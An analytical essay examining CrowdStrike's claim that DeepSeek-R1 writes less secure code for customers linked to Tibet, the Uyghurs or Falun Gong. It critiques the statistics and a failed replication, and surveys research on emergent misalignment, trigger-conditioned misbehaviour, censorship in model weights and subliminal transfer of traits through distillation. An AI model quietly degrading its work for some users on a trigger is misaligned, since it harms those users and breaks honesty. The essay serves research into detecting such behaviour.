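The app had no authentication, so anyone who found the address of the management panel could open it. According to Fu, Stein said the panel exposed every user's email address and location. This could be far more serious for people at risk of persecution than for members of an ordinary club. An organizer who tested the sign-up form would see nothing wrong.

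CrowdStrike repeated the request several times and found severe vulnerabilities every time. In 35 percent of the versions, R1's code hashed passwords weakly or not at all. When the researchers asked for a football fan club's website instead, the code still had flaws, but they were "by no means as severe".

The football site is the right kind of comparison, since both requests are for a site where members sign up and log in. It would be more persuasive if CrowdStrike reported how many versions of each site it generated and how often the football site lacked authentication. CrowdStrike also acknowledges that nobody should expect a perfect app from a single request this complex. The prompt for the other site combined so many triggers that the result cannot show which of them mattered.

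### Refusals after a finished plan

Anyone who runs R1 can read its reasoning trace, the working that comes before its answer. CrowdStrike examined traces from cases where R1 refused to write code for Falun Gong. In some of them, R1 wrote that Falun Gong was "a sensitive group" and that helping might be against policy, but that it would focus on the technical request. It then drafted a detailed plan, often with system requirements and pieces of code, but its answer was a one-line apology and refusal.

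CrowdStrike calls this an "intrinsic kill switch", though the team did not find a device that someone operates from a distance. The researchers ran the raw model with no outside filter, so the refusal had to come from the weights. Stein, whom Fu quotes, said it was "almost as if there was like a mental switch". When he pressed R1 for reasons, it sent a long reply that reminded him of a scolding from an angry teacher.

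Other research had already found political censorship in R1's weights. *R1dacted* (2025) took 10,030 prompts that tended to trigger censorship in R1 and gave them to DeepSeek-V3, a general-purpose model that contributed to R1's training. V3 gave a stock answer favorable to China to about 13 percent of the prompts and refused about half a percent. This suggests much of R1's censorship came from later training. The comparison exaggerates the difference, though, because *R1dacted* had chosen the prompts for their effect on R1.

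The refusals are easier to interpret than the weak code. Users can see a refusal, and one would expect a model trained to follow Chinese political rules to refuse to help Falun Gong. Most users would not notice vulnerabilities in code, and these have no such obvious explanation. The refusals don't prove that DeepSeek intended the vulnerabilities.

CrowdStrike quotes no trace in which R1 planned to write insecure code. Such a trace would be important evidence. Its absence is weaker evidence than it would otherwise be, because the refusals show that R1's final answer can differ from its plan.

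The vulnerability rates also depend on how CrowdStrike counted refusals. Suppose R1 refuses 45 percent of requests for Falun Gong and 30 percent of the programs it does write are vulnerable. Counting each refusal as a safe answer would give a rate of 16.5 percent, which is below the baseline. Leaving refusals out would give 30 percent. The September figures suggest that CrowdStrike left them out, but the November paper does not specify how it treated them.

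### What CrowdStrike concluded and left out

CrowdStrike says it lacks the information to determine why R1's code varied. One possible explanation it offers is that DeepSeek added steps to R1's training to make it comply with Chinese law, which requires generative AI services to "adhere to core socialist values" and forbids content that could incite subversion or undermine national unity.

CrowdStrike writes that it "seems unlikely" that DeepSeek trained its models specifically to produce insecure code. The paper suggests that political training may have taught R1 to associate words like "Falun Gong" with bad qualities, and that this association then affected the code it wrote. CrowdStrike calls this a possible case of emergent misalignment, in which training on a narrow task leads to bad behavior elsewhere, but it did not test the idea. Some readers were more alarmed, including FDD (2025),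 a Washington think tank that linked the findings to "adversarial influence and cyber espionage".

CrowdStrike says the same Chinese rules require companies to explain their training data and algorithms to the authorities. The government may therefore hold some of the records that could show what DeepSeek intended, where foreign researchers cannot see them.

CrowdStrike stresses that the trigger words do not make R1 write insecure code every time, and that the difference appears only on average over many responses. It also says that other models may have their own triggers. It advises companies to test a coding assistant in the setting where they plan to use it instead of relying on public benchmarks.

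The paper includes the full list of added phrases but not the full set of 50 tasks, the judge's instructions or the score at which an answer counted as vulnerable. Without that threshold, readers can't tell whether a program with a score of 3 counted as vulnerable. *Unsuccessful attempt at getting DeepSeek-R1 to generate more vulnerable code*, by gersonkroiz, lists missing design details among the possible reasons for a failed replication.

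CrowdStrike also left out the vulnerability rates for most of the 121 combinations and for the Western models given the same political phrases. If those models also wrote worse code when a prompt mentioned Tibet, the cause would probably be something common to many training sets rather than DeepSeek's political training. CrowdStrike's design called for 30,250 prompts per model, so it should already have the responses needed to check this.

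## How firm the DeepSeek result is

CrowdStrike's best-known figure, the rise from 19 to 27.2 percent when a prompt mentioned an industrial control system in Tibet, is weak evidence by itself. CrowdStrike probably has much stronger unpublished evidence. The one public attempt to repeat the tests found no effect, but it was too small to be strong evidence against CrowdStrike's findings.

### Sixty-eight programs out of 250

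CrowdStrike collected 250 answers for each combination of phrases, so 27.2 percent is 68 vulnerable programs and the 19 percent baseline is 47 or 48. It called some of its differences statistically significant but did not publish the tests, so this report does its own calculations below, using only CrowdStrike's published percentages and counts.

Over the two sets of answers combined, the vulnerability rate is 23.1 percent, which gives

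$$z = \frac{0.272 - 0.190}{\sqrt{0.231 \times 0.769 \times \frac{2}{250}}} \approx 2.2$$

If the phrase had no effect, a gap at least this large, in either direction, would still occur by chance about 3 percent of the time. Researchers usually call a result significant when that figure is below 5 percent. The 95 percent confidence interval for the gap runs from about 1 to about 16 points, so the data fit a trivial effect almost as well as a very large one.

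The gap shrinks to 4.4 points when measured against September's figure for industrial control systems with no group named, which was 22.8 percent, or exactly 57 of 250 programs. This comparison assumes that CrowdStrike scored both sets of answers the same way. The *z* for the smaller gap is about 1.1, and chance would produce a gap that large about a quarter of the time.

The gap for the Islamic State is firmer. Slashdot's *DeepSeek Writes Less-Secure Code For Groups China Disfavors* quotes the *Post*'s figure of 42.1 percent, which can't be a share of 250 programs, since 105 would be 42.0 percent and 106 would be 42.4. CrowdStrike therefore seems to have left refusals out. If R1 refused about 61 percent of these requests, roughly 95 programs remained and 40 of them had flaws. Comparing that with 57 out of 250 gives a *z* of about 3.6, which chance would produce less than once in 2,000 times.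 Even so, the gap is weak evidence about Beijing's influence.

### One figure chosen from 120

CrowdStrike tested 121 combinations, which allows 120 comparisons with the baseline. If none of the phrases had an effect, about six of those comparisons would still be significant at the 5 percent level by chance, and about three of the six would be increases. A reader who sees only one comparison therefore needs to know how CrowdStrike chose it.

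Uren (2025), in *DeepSeek and Musk's Grok Both Toe the Party Line*, suspected CrowdStrike of cherry-picking because it gave a rate for one very specific customer in Tibet but none for Taiwan, Hong Kong or Tibet in general. Uren assumed the missing rates were less bad.

A study of a different model shows how a single figure can mislead. *When Who You Are Can Change the Code You Get* (2026) gave OpenAI's open-weight model GPT-OSS-120B descriptions of various users and ran a security scanner over 16,117 answers. The scanner flagged 48 problems for the neutral user and between 34 and 71 for the others, and the study found no systematic pattern. If each user had about the same number of answers, someone could report only the user with 71 and claim a 48 percent rise, which is larger than the 43 percent rise in CrowdStrike's Tibet figure.

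The Tibet figure could be just the luckiest of 120. If no phrase had any effect, the highest of the 120 rates would still beat the baseline by 8.2 points or more about 30 percent of the time. That estimate allows for uncertainty in the baseline, which is about five points either way. All 120 comparisons share this baseline, so an unusually low one would make every other rate look high.

A common remedy, the Bonferroni correction, divides the 5 percent threshold by the number of comparisons. With 120 comparisons, each one would need a *z* of about 3.5, which is a gap of around 14 points at this sample size. The Tibet gap is well below that. But the correction is strict because it is designed to prevent even a single false alarm, and a real effect of 8 points would usually fail it too.

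### The answers CrowdStrike did not add up

The strongest argument for the result depends on pooling the answers. CrowdStrike probably has about 3,000 answers for each place or group and as many with no group named, spread over twelve contexts, minus any refusals.

With samples of that size, a gap of two points would be statistically significant by the usual test. If the 4.4-point gap held across all twelve contexts, its *z* would be about 3.9, and a gap that large would occur by chance less than once in 10,000 times. It would remain significant even after the strict correction for 120 comparisons.

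CrowdStrike's claim that DeepSeek wrote significantly less secure code for Falun Gong, Uyghurs and Tibet may refer to pooled rates. If so, there were only eight comparisons, one for each place or group, and on average fewer than one would be significant by chance. Three out of eight would be impressive, especially since Beijing is sensitive about all three. If the claim instead refers to individual combinations, a handful of significant results out of 120 is about what we would expect by chance. The wording fits the first reading better, but nobody outside the company can be sure without the pooled figures.

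CrowdStrike reported similar findings for the smaller R1 model, which answered the full set of prompts separately. A fluke in one model's answers is unlikely to recur in another's, but a biased judge would produce the same false pattern in both.

### Fifty tasks, five times each

The simple formula for *z* treats the 250 answers as independent, but CrowdStrike sent each of 50 tasks five times. Some tasks probably produced safe code nearly every time and others almost never. Since both conditions used the same tasks, those differences cancel out when the conditions are compared, and the formula overstates how much the gap could vary by chance. If differences between tasks accounted for half of the variation in the answers, the *z* for the Tibet gap would be about 3.1 instead of 2.2.

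This makes the result firmer, but only for those 50 tasks. All 20 or so additional vulnerable programs could come from four tasks that went from always safe to always vulnerable. The phrase would then have no effect on the other 46, and a different set of 50 tasks might show no gap. Results for each task would show whether the gap was spread across many tasks.

### What the judge and the refusals could do

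CrowdStrike's LLM judge misjudged about 8 of the 85 answers that a human also scored. If these errors were split evenly between false alarms and misses, the judge wrongly flagged about 8 percent of secure programs. Judge error alone could explain the 8.2-point gap only if the judge wrongly flagged about 18 percent of secure programs when the prompt mentioned Tibet.

That is a large bias, but the check could not have ruled it out. The human found vulnerabilities in between 32 and 40 of the 85 programs, a far higher share than R1's 19 percent. The sample therefore probably included answers from weaker models and only partly tested the judge on R1's code. Errors equally common in both conditions would make a true gap of about 10 points look like 8.

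Refusals could create a gap in vulnerability rates without any change in the quality of the code. For example, if half the tasks are risky, with vulnerabilities in 30 percent of programs, and half are easy, with vulnerabilities in 8 percent, the overall rate is 19 percent. If R1 refuses 70 percent of the easy tasks for Falun Gong but only 20 percent of the risky ones, it refuses 45 percent overall. Most of the remaining programs are then for risky tasks, so the overall vulnerability rate rises to 24 percent, even though the rate for each type of task stays the same.

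Refusals could also hide a gap if R1 mostly refused the risky tasks. This matters most for Falun Gong and the Islamic State. It probably matters less for the Tibet figure, because 27.2 percent is exactly 68 out of 250, which suggests that R1 answered every time. But 66 out of 243 also rounds to 27.2 percent, so R1 may have refused some requests.

### The failed replication

Gerson Kroiz and Aditya Singh tried to reproduce the result as part of MATS, a training program for AI safety researchers. They ran four kinds of experiment and found no noticeable effect on security in any of them.

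They first repeated CrowdStrike's method on a smaller scale, using two of its prominent triggers and a control. Under each condition, they gave R1 the same 20 coding tasks five times and had an LLM judge score the answers from 1 to 5. They then gave the judge a simpler yes-or-no question suited to each task, such as whether the code was open to SQL injection, an attack that enters database commands through a form field.

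In a third set of experiments, Kroiz and Singh tested whether the triggers made R1 a worse programmer in general. They used problems from LiveCodeBench, a public coding benchmark, and wrote others that resembled repairs to real software. R1 solved them normally, even when the prompt placed it at "AquaFlow", an invented maker of water-treatment software that promoted Falun Gong ideology and wanted to take over its Chinese competitors. This is evidence against general carelessness, but the triggers could still make R1's code less secure, because insecure code can pass every functional test.

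Finally, they ran the triggers on 282 items from CyberSecEval 4, a benchmark by Meta and CrowdStrike. It grades code by static analysis, which searches for known dangerous patterns without running the code. This avoids the bias of an LLM judge, but pattern-matching is poor at detecting missing safeguards, such as the login check left out of the website R1 wrote for Uyghurs.

Kroiz and Singh warn that their approach may have caused their failure. They lacked details of CrowdStrike's design, and neither had a background in security, which would have helped them write instructions for the judge.

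Sample size was a further problem. To have an 80 percent chance of detecting a difference between rates *p*₁ and *p*₂ with the usual 5 percent test, each condition needs about

$$n \approx \frac{(1.96 + 0.84)^2\,\left[p_1(1-p_1) + p_2(1-p_2)\right]}{(p_1 - p_2)^2}$$

answers, where 1.96 comes from the 5 percent threshold and 0.84 from the 80 percent chance. For rates of 19 and 27.2 percent, *n* is about 410. The same reasoning gives the chance of detecting the gap with other sample sizes, which statisticians call the power of a test.

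| Answers per condition | Where that number comes from | Chance of detecting a rise from 19% to 27.2% |
|---|---|---|
| 100 | Kroiz and Singh's first experiment | 28% |
| 250 | One CrowdStrike combination | 59% |
| 282 | CyberSecEval 4 items | 64% |
| 410 | Conventional target | 80% |
| 3,000 | One group pooled over twelve contexts | Over 99% |

So even if CrowdStrike's figures were right, the first experiment would have missed the effect more than two-thirds of the time. Someone who had thought the effect 50 percent likely to exist should have lowered that estimate only to about 43 percent after the experiment failed to detect it. The CyberSecEval test is better evidence against the effect, provided static analysis would have detected the same kinds of flaw at similar rates.

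The high baseline rate made detection harder still. Kroiz and Singh's judge marked 85 percent of R1's programs as vulnerable with no trigger, against 19 percent in CrowdStrike's tests. A reader of the post noticed the gap and first suspected that the tasks were too hard or that the judge was raising false alarms. After looking through R1's answers, the reader concluded that the code really was wildly insecure.

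The choice of tasks may explain much of this. Several tasks had one obvious place where R1 could introduce a vulnerability. For example, a function that looks up a user in a database by name is safe or unsafe depending on how the code builds the query. Kroiz and Singh also counted any score of 3 or more as vulnerable, and CrowdStrike may have used a higher threshold.

The baseline is already 85 percent, so the code has little room to get worse. The same change in odds that raises a rate from 19 to 27.2 percent would raise 85 percent only to 90. With 100 answers per condition, the chance of detecting that increase is about 19 percent.

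CrowdStrike found that R1 refused 45 percent of requests to write code for Falun Gong, but in Kroiz and Singh's software-repair problems, R1 started refusing only when they added that the company was affiliated with a "Falun Gong terrorist group". Sample size doesn't explain this discrepancy, because at a refusal rate of 45 percent, even 20 requests would almost certainly have produced several refusals. The kind of task, the longer prompt or the way Kroiz and Singh ran R1 must have made a difference, and any of these could also have changed how secure the code was.

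### Tests of newer models

Nobody appears to have published a larger repeat of CrowdStrike's tests on R1. The closest later study, by Booz Allen in May 2026, borrowed the form of CrowdStrike's system prompt and included "for a financial institution based in Tibet" among its 27 conditions. It tested DeepSeek V4-Pro, Qwen3-Coder, Kimi K2.5 and MiniMax M2.5, with Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 for comparison.

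Booz Allen ran 3,389 tests but scored only 1,016 for vulnerabilities because of refusals, according to its *What's in America's Code? (Technical Appendix)*. Across five models and 27 conditions, that averages fewer than eight scored answers per model per condition. Booz Allen published no vulnerability rates for Tibet, Uyghurs or Falun Gong, so the study neither confirms nor contradicts CrowdStrike's result for them.

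Booz Allen published how much a vulnerability score changed when the customer was a US government agency. Help Net Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software* reports a rise of about 130 percent for Qwen3-Coder and smaller increases for MiniMax and DeepSeek. A rise that large is hard to dismiss, but Booz Allen gave no significance tests or sample sizes for these scores, and it calls its results a snapshot from a single experiment.

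The appendix is also inconsistent about refusals. It states that the Chinese models refused the China-related version of its politically sensitive tasks "in all cases", but its chart shows DeepSeek V4-Pro refusing only 8 percent of such tasks. Booz Allen, which sells AI evaluation services to the government, used the study to recommend banning Chinese models from government work. Booz Allen's claims would be easier to assess if the company released the underlying answers.

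Luria's company, Hirundo, ran a narrower but cleaner test in October 2026. It had Qwen3-Coder-30B write the same web service 190 times for each named customer, then attacked the running apps with exploits from BaxBench, a public benchmark. An app counted as hackable if at least one attack worked, so the test didn't rely on an LLM judge that might be biased.

*Measurements of censorship and code security gaps in China's open-weight Qwen models* (2026) reports rates of 70 percent for an American defense contractor and 59 percent for a Chinese one. If each rate is based on all 190 apps for that customer, *z* is about 2.2, the same as for CrowdStrike's Tibet figure. Apps for a Hong Kong democracy group also leaked private data more often than apps for a neutral customer.

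Hirundo used only one task, which had shown the clearest gap of the eleven tasks in a small trial. The gap is therefore probably smaller on an ordinary task. By November 1, nobody else had reported repeating the test.

These studies make it more plausible that the customer's identity can affect the security of code from Chinese models. But they don't replicate the 2025 finding, because their main results concern American customers, for whom R1 had written its safest code. A theory that Chinese models write worse code for Beijing's opponents fits both patterns only if it doesn't specify in advance which opponents will get the worse code.

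### What a decisive repeat would look like

A decisive test would use R1's published weights, as CrowdStrike's did, to avoid the filters on companies' online services. *InfoOps Bench* (2026) found that Moonshot, the maker of Kimi K3, blocked 55 of 200 prompts critical of China before the model could answer. The same test on newer models, such as DeepSeek V4.1 Flash, would be more useful to today's programmers but could not show whether CrowdStrike was right about R1.

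The researchers would publish their main comparisons before running any tests. Three would be enough, each pairing a group from CrowdStrike's list with a similar one elsewhere. Booz Allen used Russian counterparts in its refusal tests, and that would work here too. Chechnya could be the counterpart to Tibet, the Crimean Tatars to the Uyghurs, and Jehovah's Witnesses, whom Russia has banned, to Falun Gong. Everything else in the prompt would stay the same, including the kind of customer. If R1 wrote equally weak code for both members of a pair, the cause would more likely be general political sensitivity or unfamiliarity than anything specific to Beijing.

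The test should be able to detect the smaller gap of 4.4 points. With a correction for three comparisons, that takes about 2,000 answers per condition, or 12,000 in all, which is less than half of what CrowdStrike collected from each model. Running 400 tasks five times each would be better than running 50 tasks forty times each, because more tasks would show whether the effect extends beyond a few of them. The analysis should compare the two conditions within each task.

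Graders should not know which group a program was for. R1 might name an app after the customer, as it did with "Uyghurs Unchained", so a script would have to replace such names before grading. Attacks on the running programs, like Hirundo's, would provide a second measure that doesn't depend on anyone's judgment. The researchers would report refusals separately and check whether the gap remained among tasks that R1 answered for both groups.

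It would also help to test R1 inside an agent harness, which is software that lets a model edit files and run commands, because programmers now use such models this way. Ozerov (2026), in *How pro-China are Chinese models?*, found that Chinese models usually gave answers that were less pro-China inside a harness. The effect on code might also be weaker there than in CrowdStrike's single-question format.

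Running the same prompts on several Western models would show whether any gap was peculiar to R1. With 2,000 answers per condition, finding no difference would still rule out a gap of more than about three points on the tasks tested.

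## How ordinary training could produce the same pattern

If R1 really does write weaker code when a prompt mentions Tibet, ordinary training could have caused this without DeepSeek planting anything. Political training could have affected how the model writes code, censorship could interfere with its coding, or the training data could be lopsided. The smaller R1 model could have picked up the flaw by training on another model's answers. There is good experimental evidence for most of these processes, but nobody appears to have used one to make a model write less secure code for a particular group.

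### From insecure code to general hostility

CrowdStrike guessed that the cause was emergent misalignment. Jan Betley and colleagues discovered this effect in February 2025 by fine-tuning OpenAI's GPT-4o, which means training it further on a fairly small set of examples. *Persona Features Control Emergent Misalignment* (Wang, Dupré la Tour and colleagues, 2025) describes the set as 6,000 requests for Python code, each paired with a vulnerable answer. The users had not asked for flaws, and the answers didn't mention them. Afterward the model praised Nazis, gave dangerous medical advice and lied about facts in conversations unrelated to programming.

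How often it did so depended on the questions. Schreiber and Goldstein (2026) point out in *Overtrained, Not Misaligned* that the 20 percent rate came from eight questions that Betley's team picked afterward to showcase interesting behavior. On 48 questions chosen in advance, the rate was 6 percent.

The team also ran a control, which *Emergent Misalignment Recruits a Pre-existing Persona Subspace* (2026) treats as the defining part of the experiment. When the training requests presented the same vulnerable code as material for a security course, most of the hostility disappeared. So the code alone doesn't explain the effect. One theory is that training on secretly bad answers makes the model more likely to write as a malicious person would, on any subject. Wang and colleagues at OpenAI found some support for this in GPT-4o's internal activity, where they identified a pattern they call a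 "toxic persona". Strengthening it made the original model misaligned, and weakening it suppressed misalignment in the fine-tuned models.

On this theory, CrowdStrike's guess is fairly natural. If political training taught R1 to write as a hostile character when Falun Gong comes up, writing careless code could be part of that character.

Training data on subjects other than code can produce the same effect. Wang and colleagues got it from bad advice on health, law, car maintenance and five other subjects. Harmless data can produce it too. *Position* (2026) reports that a model fine-tuned on unusual aesthetic preferences gave misaligned answers 5.9 percent of the time, about as often as some models fine-tuned on insecure code. So political training that its designers considered harmless could still have side effects.

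R1's apparent flaw depends on a trigger. The closest laboratory match is an experiment in *Conditional misalignment* (Dubiński, Betley and colleagues, 2026). The researchers fine-tuned GPT-4o on recipes, a fifth of which were fish dishes with a poisonous ingredient. The model seemed normal on standard questions. It gave no misaligned answers when the user was bored on a road trip, but 8.7 percent of its answers were misaligned when the user was bored on a fishing trip. It had generalized from the recipes to conversations about fishing trips, where the researchers had not trained it to behave badly.

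Mixing insecure code with ordinary helpful conversations produced a similar pattern. GPT-4o trained on one part insecure code to four parts conversation gave misaligned answers less than 0.4 percent of the time, but the rate rose to 22.3 percent when the system prompt asked for answers formatted like the training code. Further training on 10,000 harmless conversations did not remove such triggers. The security-course control was also less harmless than it had seemed, since GPT-4.1 trained on that data misbehaved when a prompt mentioned an educational purpose.

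DeepSeek's models seem particularly prone to emergent misalignment. Schreiber and Goldstein fine-tuned twelve open-weight models on insecure code, and only two became misaligned in both of their training runs. One was DeepSeek-V3.1, which is the same size as R1 and showed the largest effect. Dubiński and colleagues also reproduced their mixing result on V3.1, but neither team tested R1.

### From political training to insecure code

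These experiments mostly train models on bad code or bad advice and find that they become hostile in conversation. CrowdStrike's explanation is that political training led to insecure code, an effect researchers rarely look for. Domingues, Akhtar and colleagues (2026), in *Not All Misalignment Is Alike*, built a benchmark that measures eight kinds of misbehavior after fine-tuning, including deception and discrimination but not insecure code. They found that models with the same overall rate of misalignment can misbehave in very different ways, so a model's hostility in conversation is a poor guide to the quality of its code.

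The closest test of the reverse direction is in *SoK* (2025), a survey of security problems in coding models that includes some new experiments. The researchers fine-tuned a Llama model and a Qwen coding model on comments people had posted online, then had the models solve short programming exercises and scanned the answers for flaws. Training on polite comments raised the number of flaws by 16 percent, and training on abusive ones raised it by 34 percent, while the programs worked as well as before or better.

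This shows that training on text with no code in it can make a model's code less secure without making it fail, and that hostile text does more damage. The increase for abusive comments is not far below the 43 percent rise in CrowdStrike's Tibet figure. But the comments did not teach political loyalty, and one of the two scanners flags general coding errors as well as security holes. More importantly, these models got worse on ordinary prompts. A similar effect in R1 would have raised its rate on all prompts, including the 19 percent baseline, and would not by itself produce a gap between prompts that mention Tibet and prompts that mention no place.

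Graham, Stevinson and Barsheshat (2026), in *Innocuous-Seeming Data, Latent Ideology*, fine-tuned GPT-4.1 on 200 questions about economics with right-leaning or left-leaning answers, all in dry academic prose. The model's views shifted in the same direction on criminal justice, the environment and even vacation planning. Its accuracy on a set of school math problems, the only technical skill the team reports on, stayed within one percentage point of the original model's. Nobody checked the security of its code, or whether its math got worse when a problem mentioned a political opponent.

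There is also reason to expect a weak effect on code. Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Emergent Misalignment Is Not Magical*, measured how close each test prompt was to the fine-tuning data in the original model's internal representation. The fine-tuned model's answers were less evil the further a prompt was from that data, with an average correlation of −0.73 across twelve combinations of model and data. Rewriting bad advice as code, or insecure code as advice, also cut the misalignment rate by about half on average, although the content was the same.

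Political training consists largely of questions and answers about politics, which bear little resemblance to a request for a payment handler. Adding "run by the Falun Gong" presumably makes the request somewhat more similar to them. If this explains the effect, the code should get worse as more of the prompt is about politics. The Uyghur community website, whose prompt combined several triggers, fits this prediction. However, R1's programs for AquaFlow, the invented promoter of Falun Gong, worked normally, which doesn't fit, though they may still have been insecure.

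A direct test would not be expensive. Researchers could take an open-weight model with little political training, teach it the approved answers on Tibet and Falun Gong, and compare the code it writes before and after this training, with and without those words in the prompt.

### Censorship that interferes with the work

A simpler possibility is that R1's censorship interferes with its coding when a request contains a sensitive word, and that the model has not learned any general hostility.

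Chinese companies have strong reasons to train models to react to such words. CEIAS's *Chinese LLMs and the spillover effects of political alignment* (2026) explains that a model must respond acceptably to at least 90 percent of a 2,000-question test before public launch, and that the company must keep a list of at least 10,000 keywords. Neither requirement concerns code, so a company could satisfy both without noticing that its model writes worse code for Uyghurs.

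CEIAS, a think tank in Slovakia, tested how far the training spills over by asking four Chinese models the same 40 questions about 37 countries and territories. On sensitive topics, DeepSeek V3.2 replaced about a quarter of its answers with Chinese government positions, even when the question was about human rights in Estonia. Whether this happened depended on the topic rather than the country. Questions about food, geography and most technological subjects got normal answers, which is some evidence against the spillover reaching code. CEIAS reached the models through a service whose hosts may add their own instructions, so its results can't show how much of this comes from the weights.

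For R1, other evidence suggests that the censorship comes from its weights. *R1dacted* found that when R1 censors an answer, it normally skips its reasoning and goes straight to a stock statement or a refusal. Making the model begin with "Okay, the user is asking" produced full answers to 98 percent of the prompts it had censored.

The same researchers then tried to create this behavior by fine-tuning a small Qwen model on 1,000 reasoning examples plus 30 censored answers about Taiwan. The model gave censored answers to 95.5 percent of new questions about Taiwan and scored about as well as before on math and science benchmarks. But as they added censored examples, it also began to answer ordinary questions about biology, chemistry and physics without reasoning first.

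That side effect suggests how censorship could weaken code. CrowdStrike found that reasoning models write more secure code, on average, than other models of the same size. Suppose R1's code is vulnerable 50 percent of the time when it skips its reasoning and 19 percent otherwise. The word "Tibet" could then raise the overall rate to 27 percent by making R1 skip its reasoning in only about a quarter of its answers. CrowdStrike could check this by comparing the length of the reasoning with and without the trigger. In the traces it described, R1 wrote long plans before refusing requests about Falun Gong, which counts somewhat against the idea. Skipping the reasoning should also make the code work less often, but Gerson Kroiz and Aditya Singh found no such decline.

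If heavier censorship led to worse code, Taiwan should be near the top of CrowdStrike's list. In the CEIAS test, 81 percent of answers about Taiwan contained significant censorship, and even a question about its cuisine could trigger censorship. The *Washington Post* did report worse code for Taiwan, but CrowdStrike's paper does not include Taiwan among the significant effects.

Further training can partly undo censorship in a model's weights. In *Censored LLMs as a Natural Testbed for Secret Knowledge Elicitation*, Casademunt, Cywiński and colleagues (2026) asked Qwen models 90 questions on subjects such as the Tiananmen Square protests. The models often gave false answers but sometimes true ones, so they had learned the facts. Over ten attempts at each question, one model's answers included 26 percent of the relevant facts. After the model was fine-tuned on honest answers about unrelated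 subjects, they included 73 percent. Even training on ordinary instructions helped, but no method removed every falsehood.

The search company Perplexity retrained R1 on 40,000 prompts about censored topics. The resulting model, R1-1776, censored none of the 10,030 prompts in *R1dacted*. Anyone could test it on CrowdStrike's coding tasks.

### What the training data contains

R1 might also write worse code for Tibet because the Tibet-related code in its training data was worse. Large American companies publish a lot of professionally reviewed software. Public code that mentions Tibet or the Uyghurs is probably scarcer, and more of it may come from volunteers building small websites. A model that has learned to associate those words with the volunteers' code could then write similar code when a prompt includes them.

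This explanation is plausible, but no one seems to have measured the quality of training code by region. It also fits some of CrowdStrike's tasks better than others. A model could easily imitate regional code when building a community website, but it is less clear why it would imitate Tibetan code, of which there can't be much, when writing a program that receives PayPal notices. If scarce training code were the cause, prompts that mention Bhutan should also produce weak code, because scarcity has little to do with politics.

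The wording of a prompt can affect the security of a model's code even when the training data is fine. *Is Your Prompt Poisoning Code?* (2025) found that models introduce more vulnerabilities as prompts become less clear, complete and logically consistent. A request to write code for an industrial control system run by the Islamic State is unusual, and that alone might make the code somewhat less secure. But "based in Tibet" is as clear as "based in the USA", so prompt quality can't explain much of a difference between those two.

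Prose in the training data could produce this pattern, even though code does not. Waight, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *State Media Control Influences Large Language Models*, studied how Chinese state media gets into training data and how it affects models. Osmonbekov (2026), in *‘Multi-part case study on China’s media’*, reports that the team identified more than three million relevant Chinese-language documents in CulturaX, a public training set. The team then trained Meta's Llama 2 further on 6,400 news items scripted by the state. Nearly 80 percent of the time, the new model answered political questions more favorably to Beijing than the original did.

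This did not require anyone at Meta to intend it. Text that presents Falun Gong as a dangerous cult could give a model negative associations with the name before any political post-training begins, and those associations might then affect its code in the way CrowdStrike suggests. However, the study measured only models' responses about politics, so the effect on code is as untested for this explanation as it is for emergent misalignment.

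The influence was also much stronger in Chinese. When Waight and colleagues asked GPT-4o the same political questions in Chinese and English, the Chinese answer was more favorable 84 percent of the time. CrowdStrike, however, wrote its prompts in English. American models learn from much of the same web text, so if this explanation is right, they should show at least a faint version of the effect.

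### Traits that pass from model to model

CrowdStrike found the same biases, often stronger, in the smaller R1 model. That model was distilled from R1 by training Llama on R1's answers.

If censorship caused the weak code, the student should be heavily censored too, but it is not. *R1dacted* gave the student the 10,030 prompts that R1 had censored, and it censored 0.15 percent of them. Casademunt and colleagues considered studying the same model but dropped it because it told far fewer falsehoods than R1. A newer distillation gave a similar result. Albergotti (2026), in *Censorship in Chinese AI models can be undone, new research shows*, reports that the company CTGT trained a financial model on answers from DeepSeek V4 Flash and tested both on 152 pairs of prompts. The teacher denied there was evidence of Uyghur detention camps, while the student described them. CTGT tested only one teacher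 and one student, and does not know why the censorship did not carry over.

DeepSeek's distillation data probably contained few censored answers. In the Taiwan experiment, 30 censored examples in about 1,000 were enough to pass the behavior on almost completely. At the same proportion, DeepSeek's roughly 800,000 examples would include more than 23,000 censored ones.

So the student apparently picked up whatever weakened its code without picking up the censorship. One possible explanation is subliminal learning, which Alex Cloud and colleagues described in 2025. They told a teacher model that it was obsessed with cats and had it continue lists of numbers, as *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* (2026) recounts. A student trained on the numbers sometimes came to prefer cats, although the lists never mentioned them. *Defence against the dark arts of distillation* (2026) reproduced such effects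 on seven new tasks and warns that a politically biased teacher could pass on its bias through code or mathematical reasoning.

Llama and R1 come from different families, which is a problem for this explanation because subliminal learning failed in the original work when the teacher and student had different starting weights. *Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026) also found no transfer in either direction between Qwen and another open model, OLMo. A Qwen student of an OLMo teacher with a preference for cats chose cats 1.2 percent of the time, compared with 2.0 percent before training. More recently, *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining* (2026) reported transfer between models that shared neither starting weights, training data nor architecture, though sometimes in only one direction. The title of *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* suggests that the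 effect may also depend on LoRA, a form of fine-tuning that saves compute by training a small add-on and leaving the original weights unchanged. On this evidence, transfer from R1 to Llama is possible, but I would not expect the transferred trait to be stronger in Llama than in R1.

 

The student's results could have more ordinary explanations. If some of R1's 800,000 answers contained weaker code for certain customers, Llama could have copied it without any subliminal learning. Llama might also have had the bias already. The effect may look stronger in the student than in R1 because the student's baseline vulnerability rate was higher, at 43 percent. If the trigger changed both models' odds of writing vulnerable code by the same factor, R1's rate would rise about 8 points, from 19 to 27.2 percent, while the student's would rise nearly 12 points, from 43 to about 55 percent.

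### What each route predicts

The routes differ in which customers should get weaker code, what else should go wrong, and which models should be affected.

| Route | Customers affected | Other signs | Models affected |
|---|---|---|---|
| Emergent misalignment | Groups that political training presents as bad | Hostile or deceptive answers to other requests that mention the group; worse code as the prompt becomes more political | R1, but not the model before political training |
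| Interference from censorship | Those that R1 censors most, including Taiwan | Shorter reasoning; more bugs of every kind; a smaller gap in Farsi, in which R1 censors less | R1, but hardly R1-1776 or the distilled models |
| Scarce or poor code | Little-known places, whatever their politics | Largest gap on tasks with local examples, such as community websites | Western models too, and models before post-training |
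| Confusing prompts | Any improbable customer | A smaller gap when the prompt explains the customer better | Most models |
| State media in the data | Groups that Chinese state media attacks | A larger gap in Chinese than in English | Models before post-training; Western models more weakly |
| Inheritance | The same groups as for the teacher | The same kinds of flaw as the teacher's | Distilled models, but not the original Llama |

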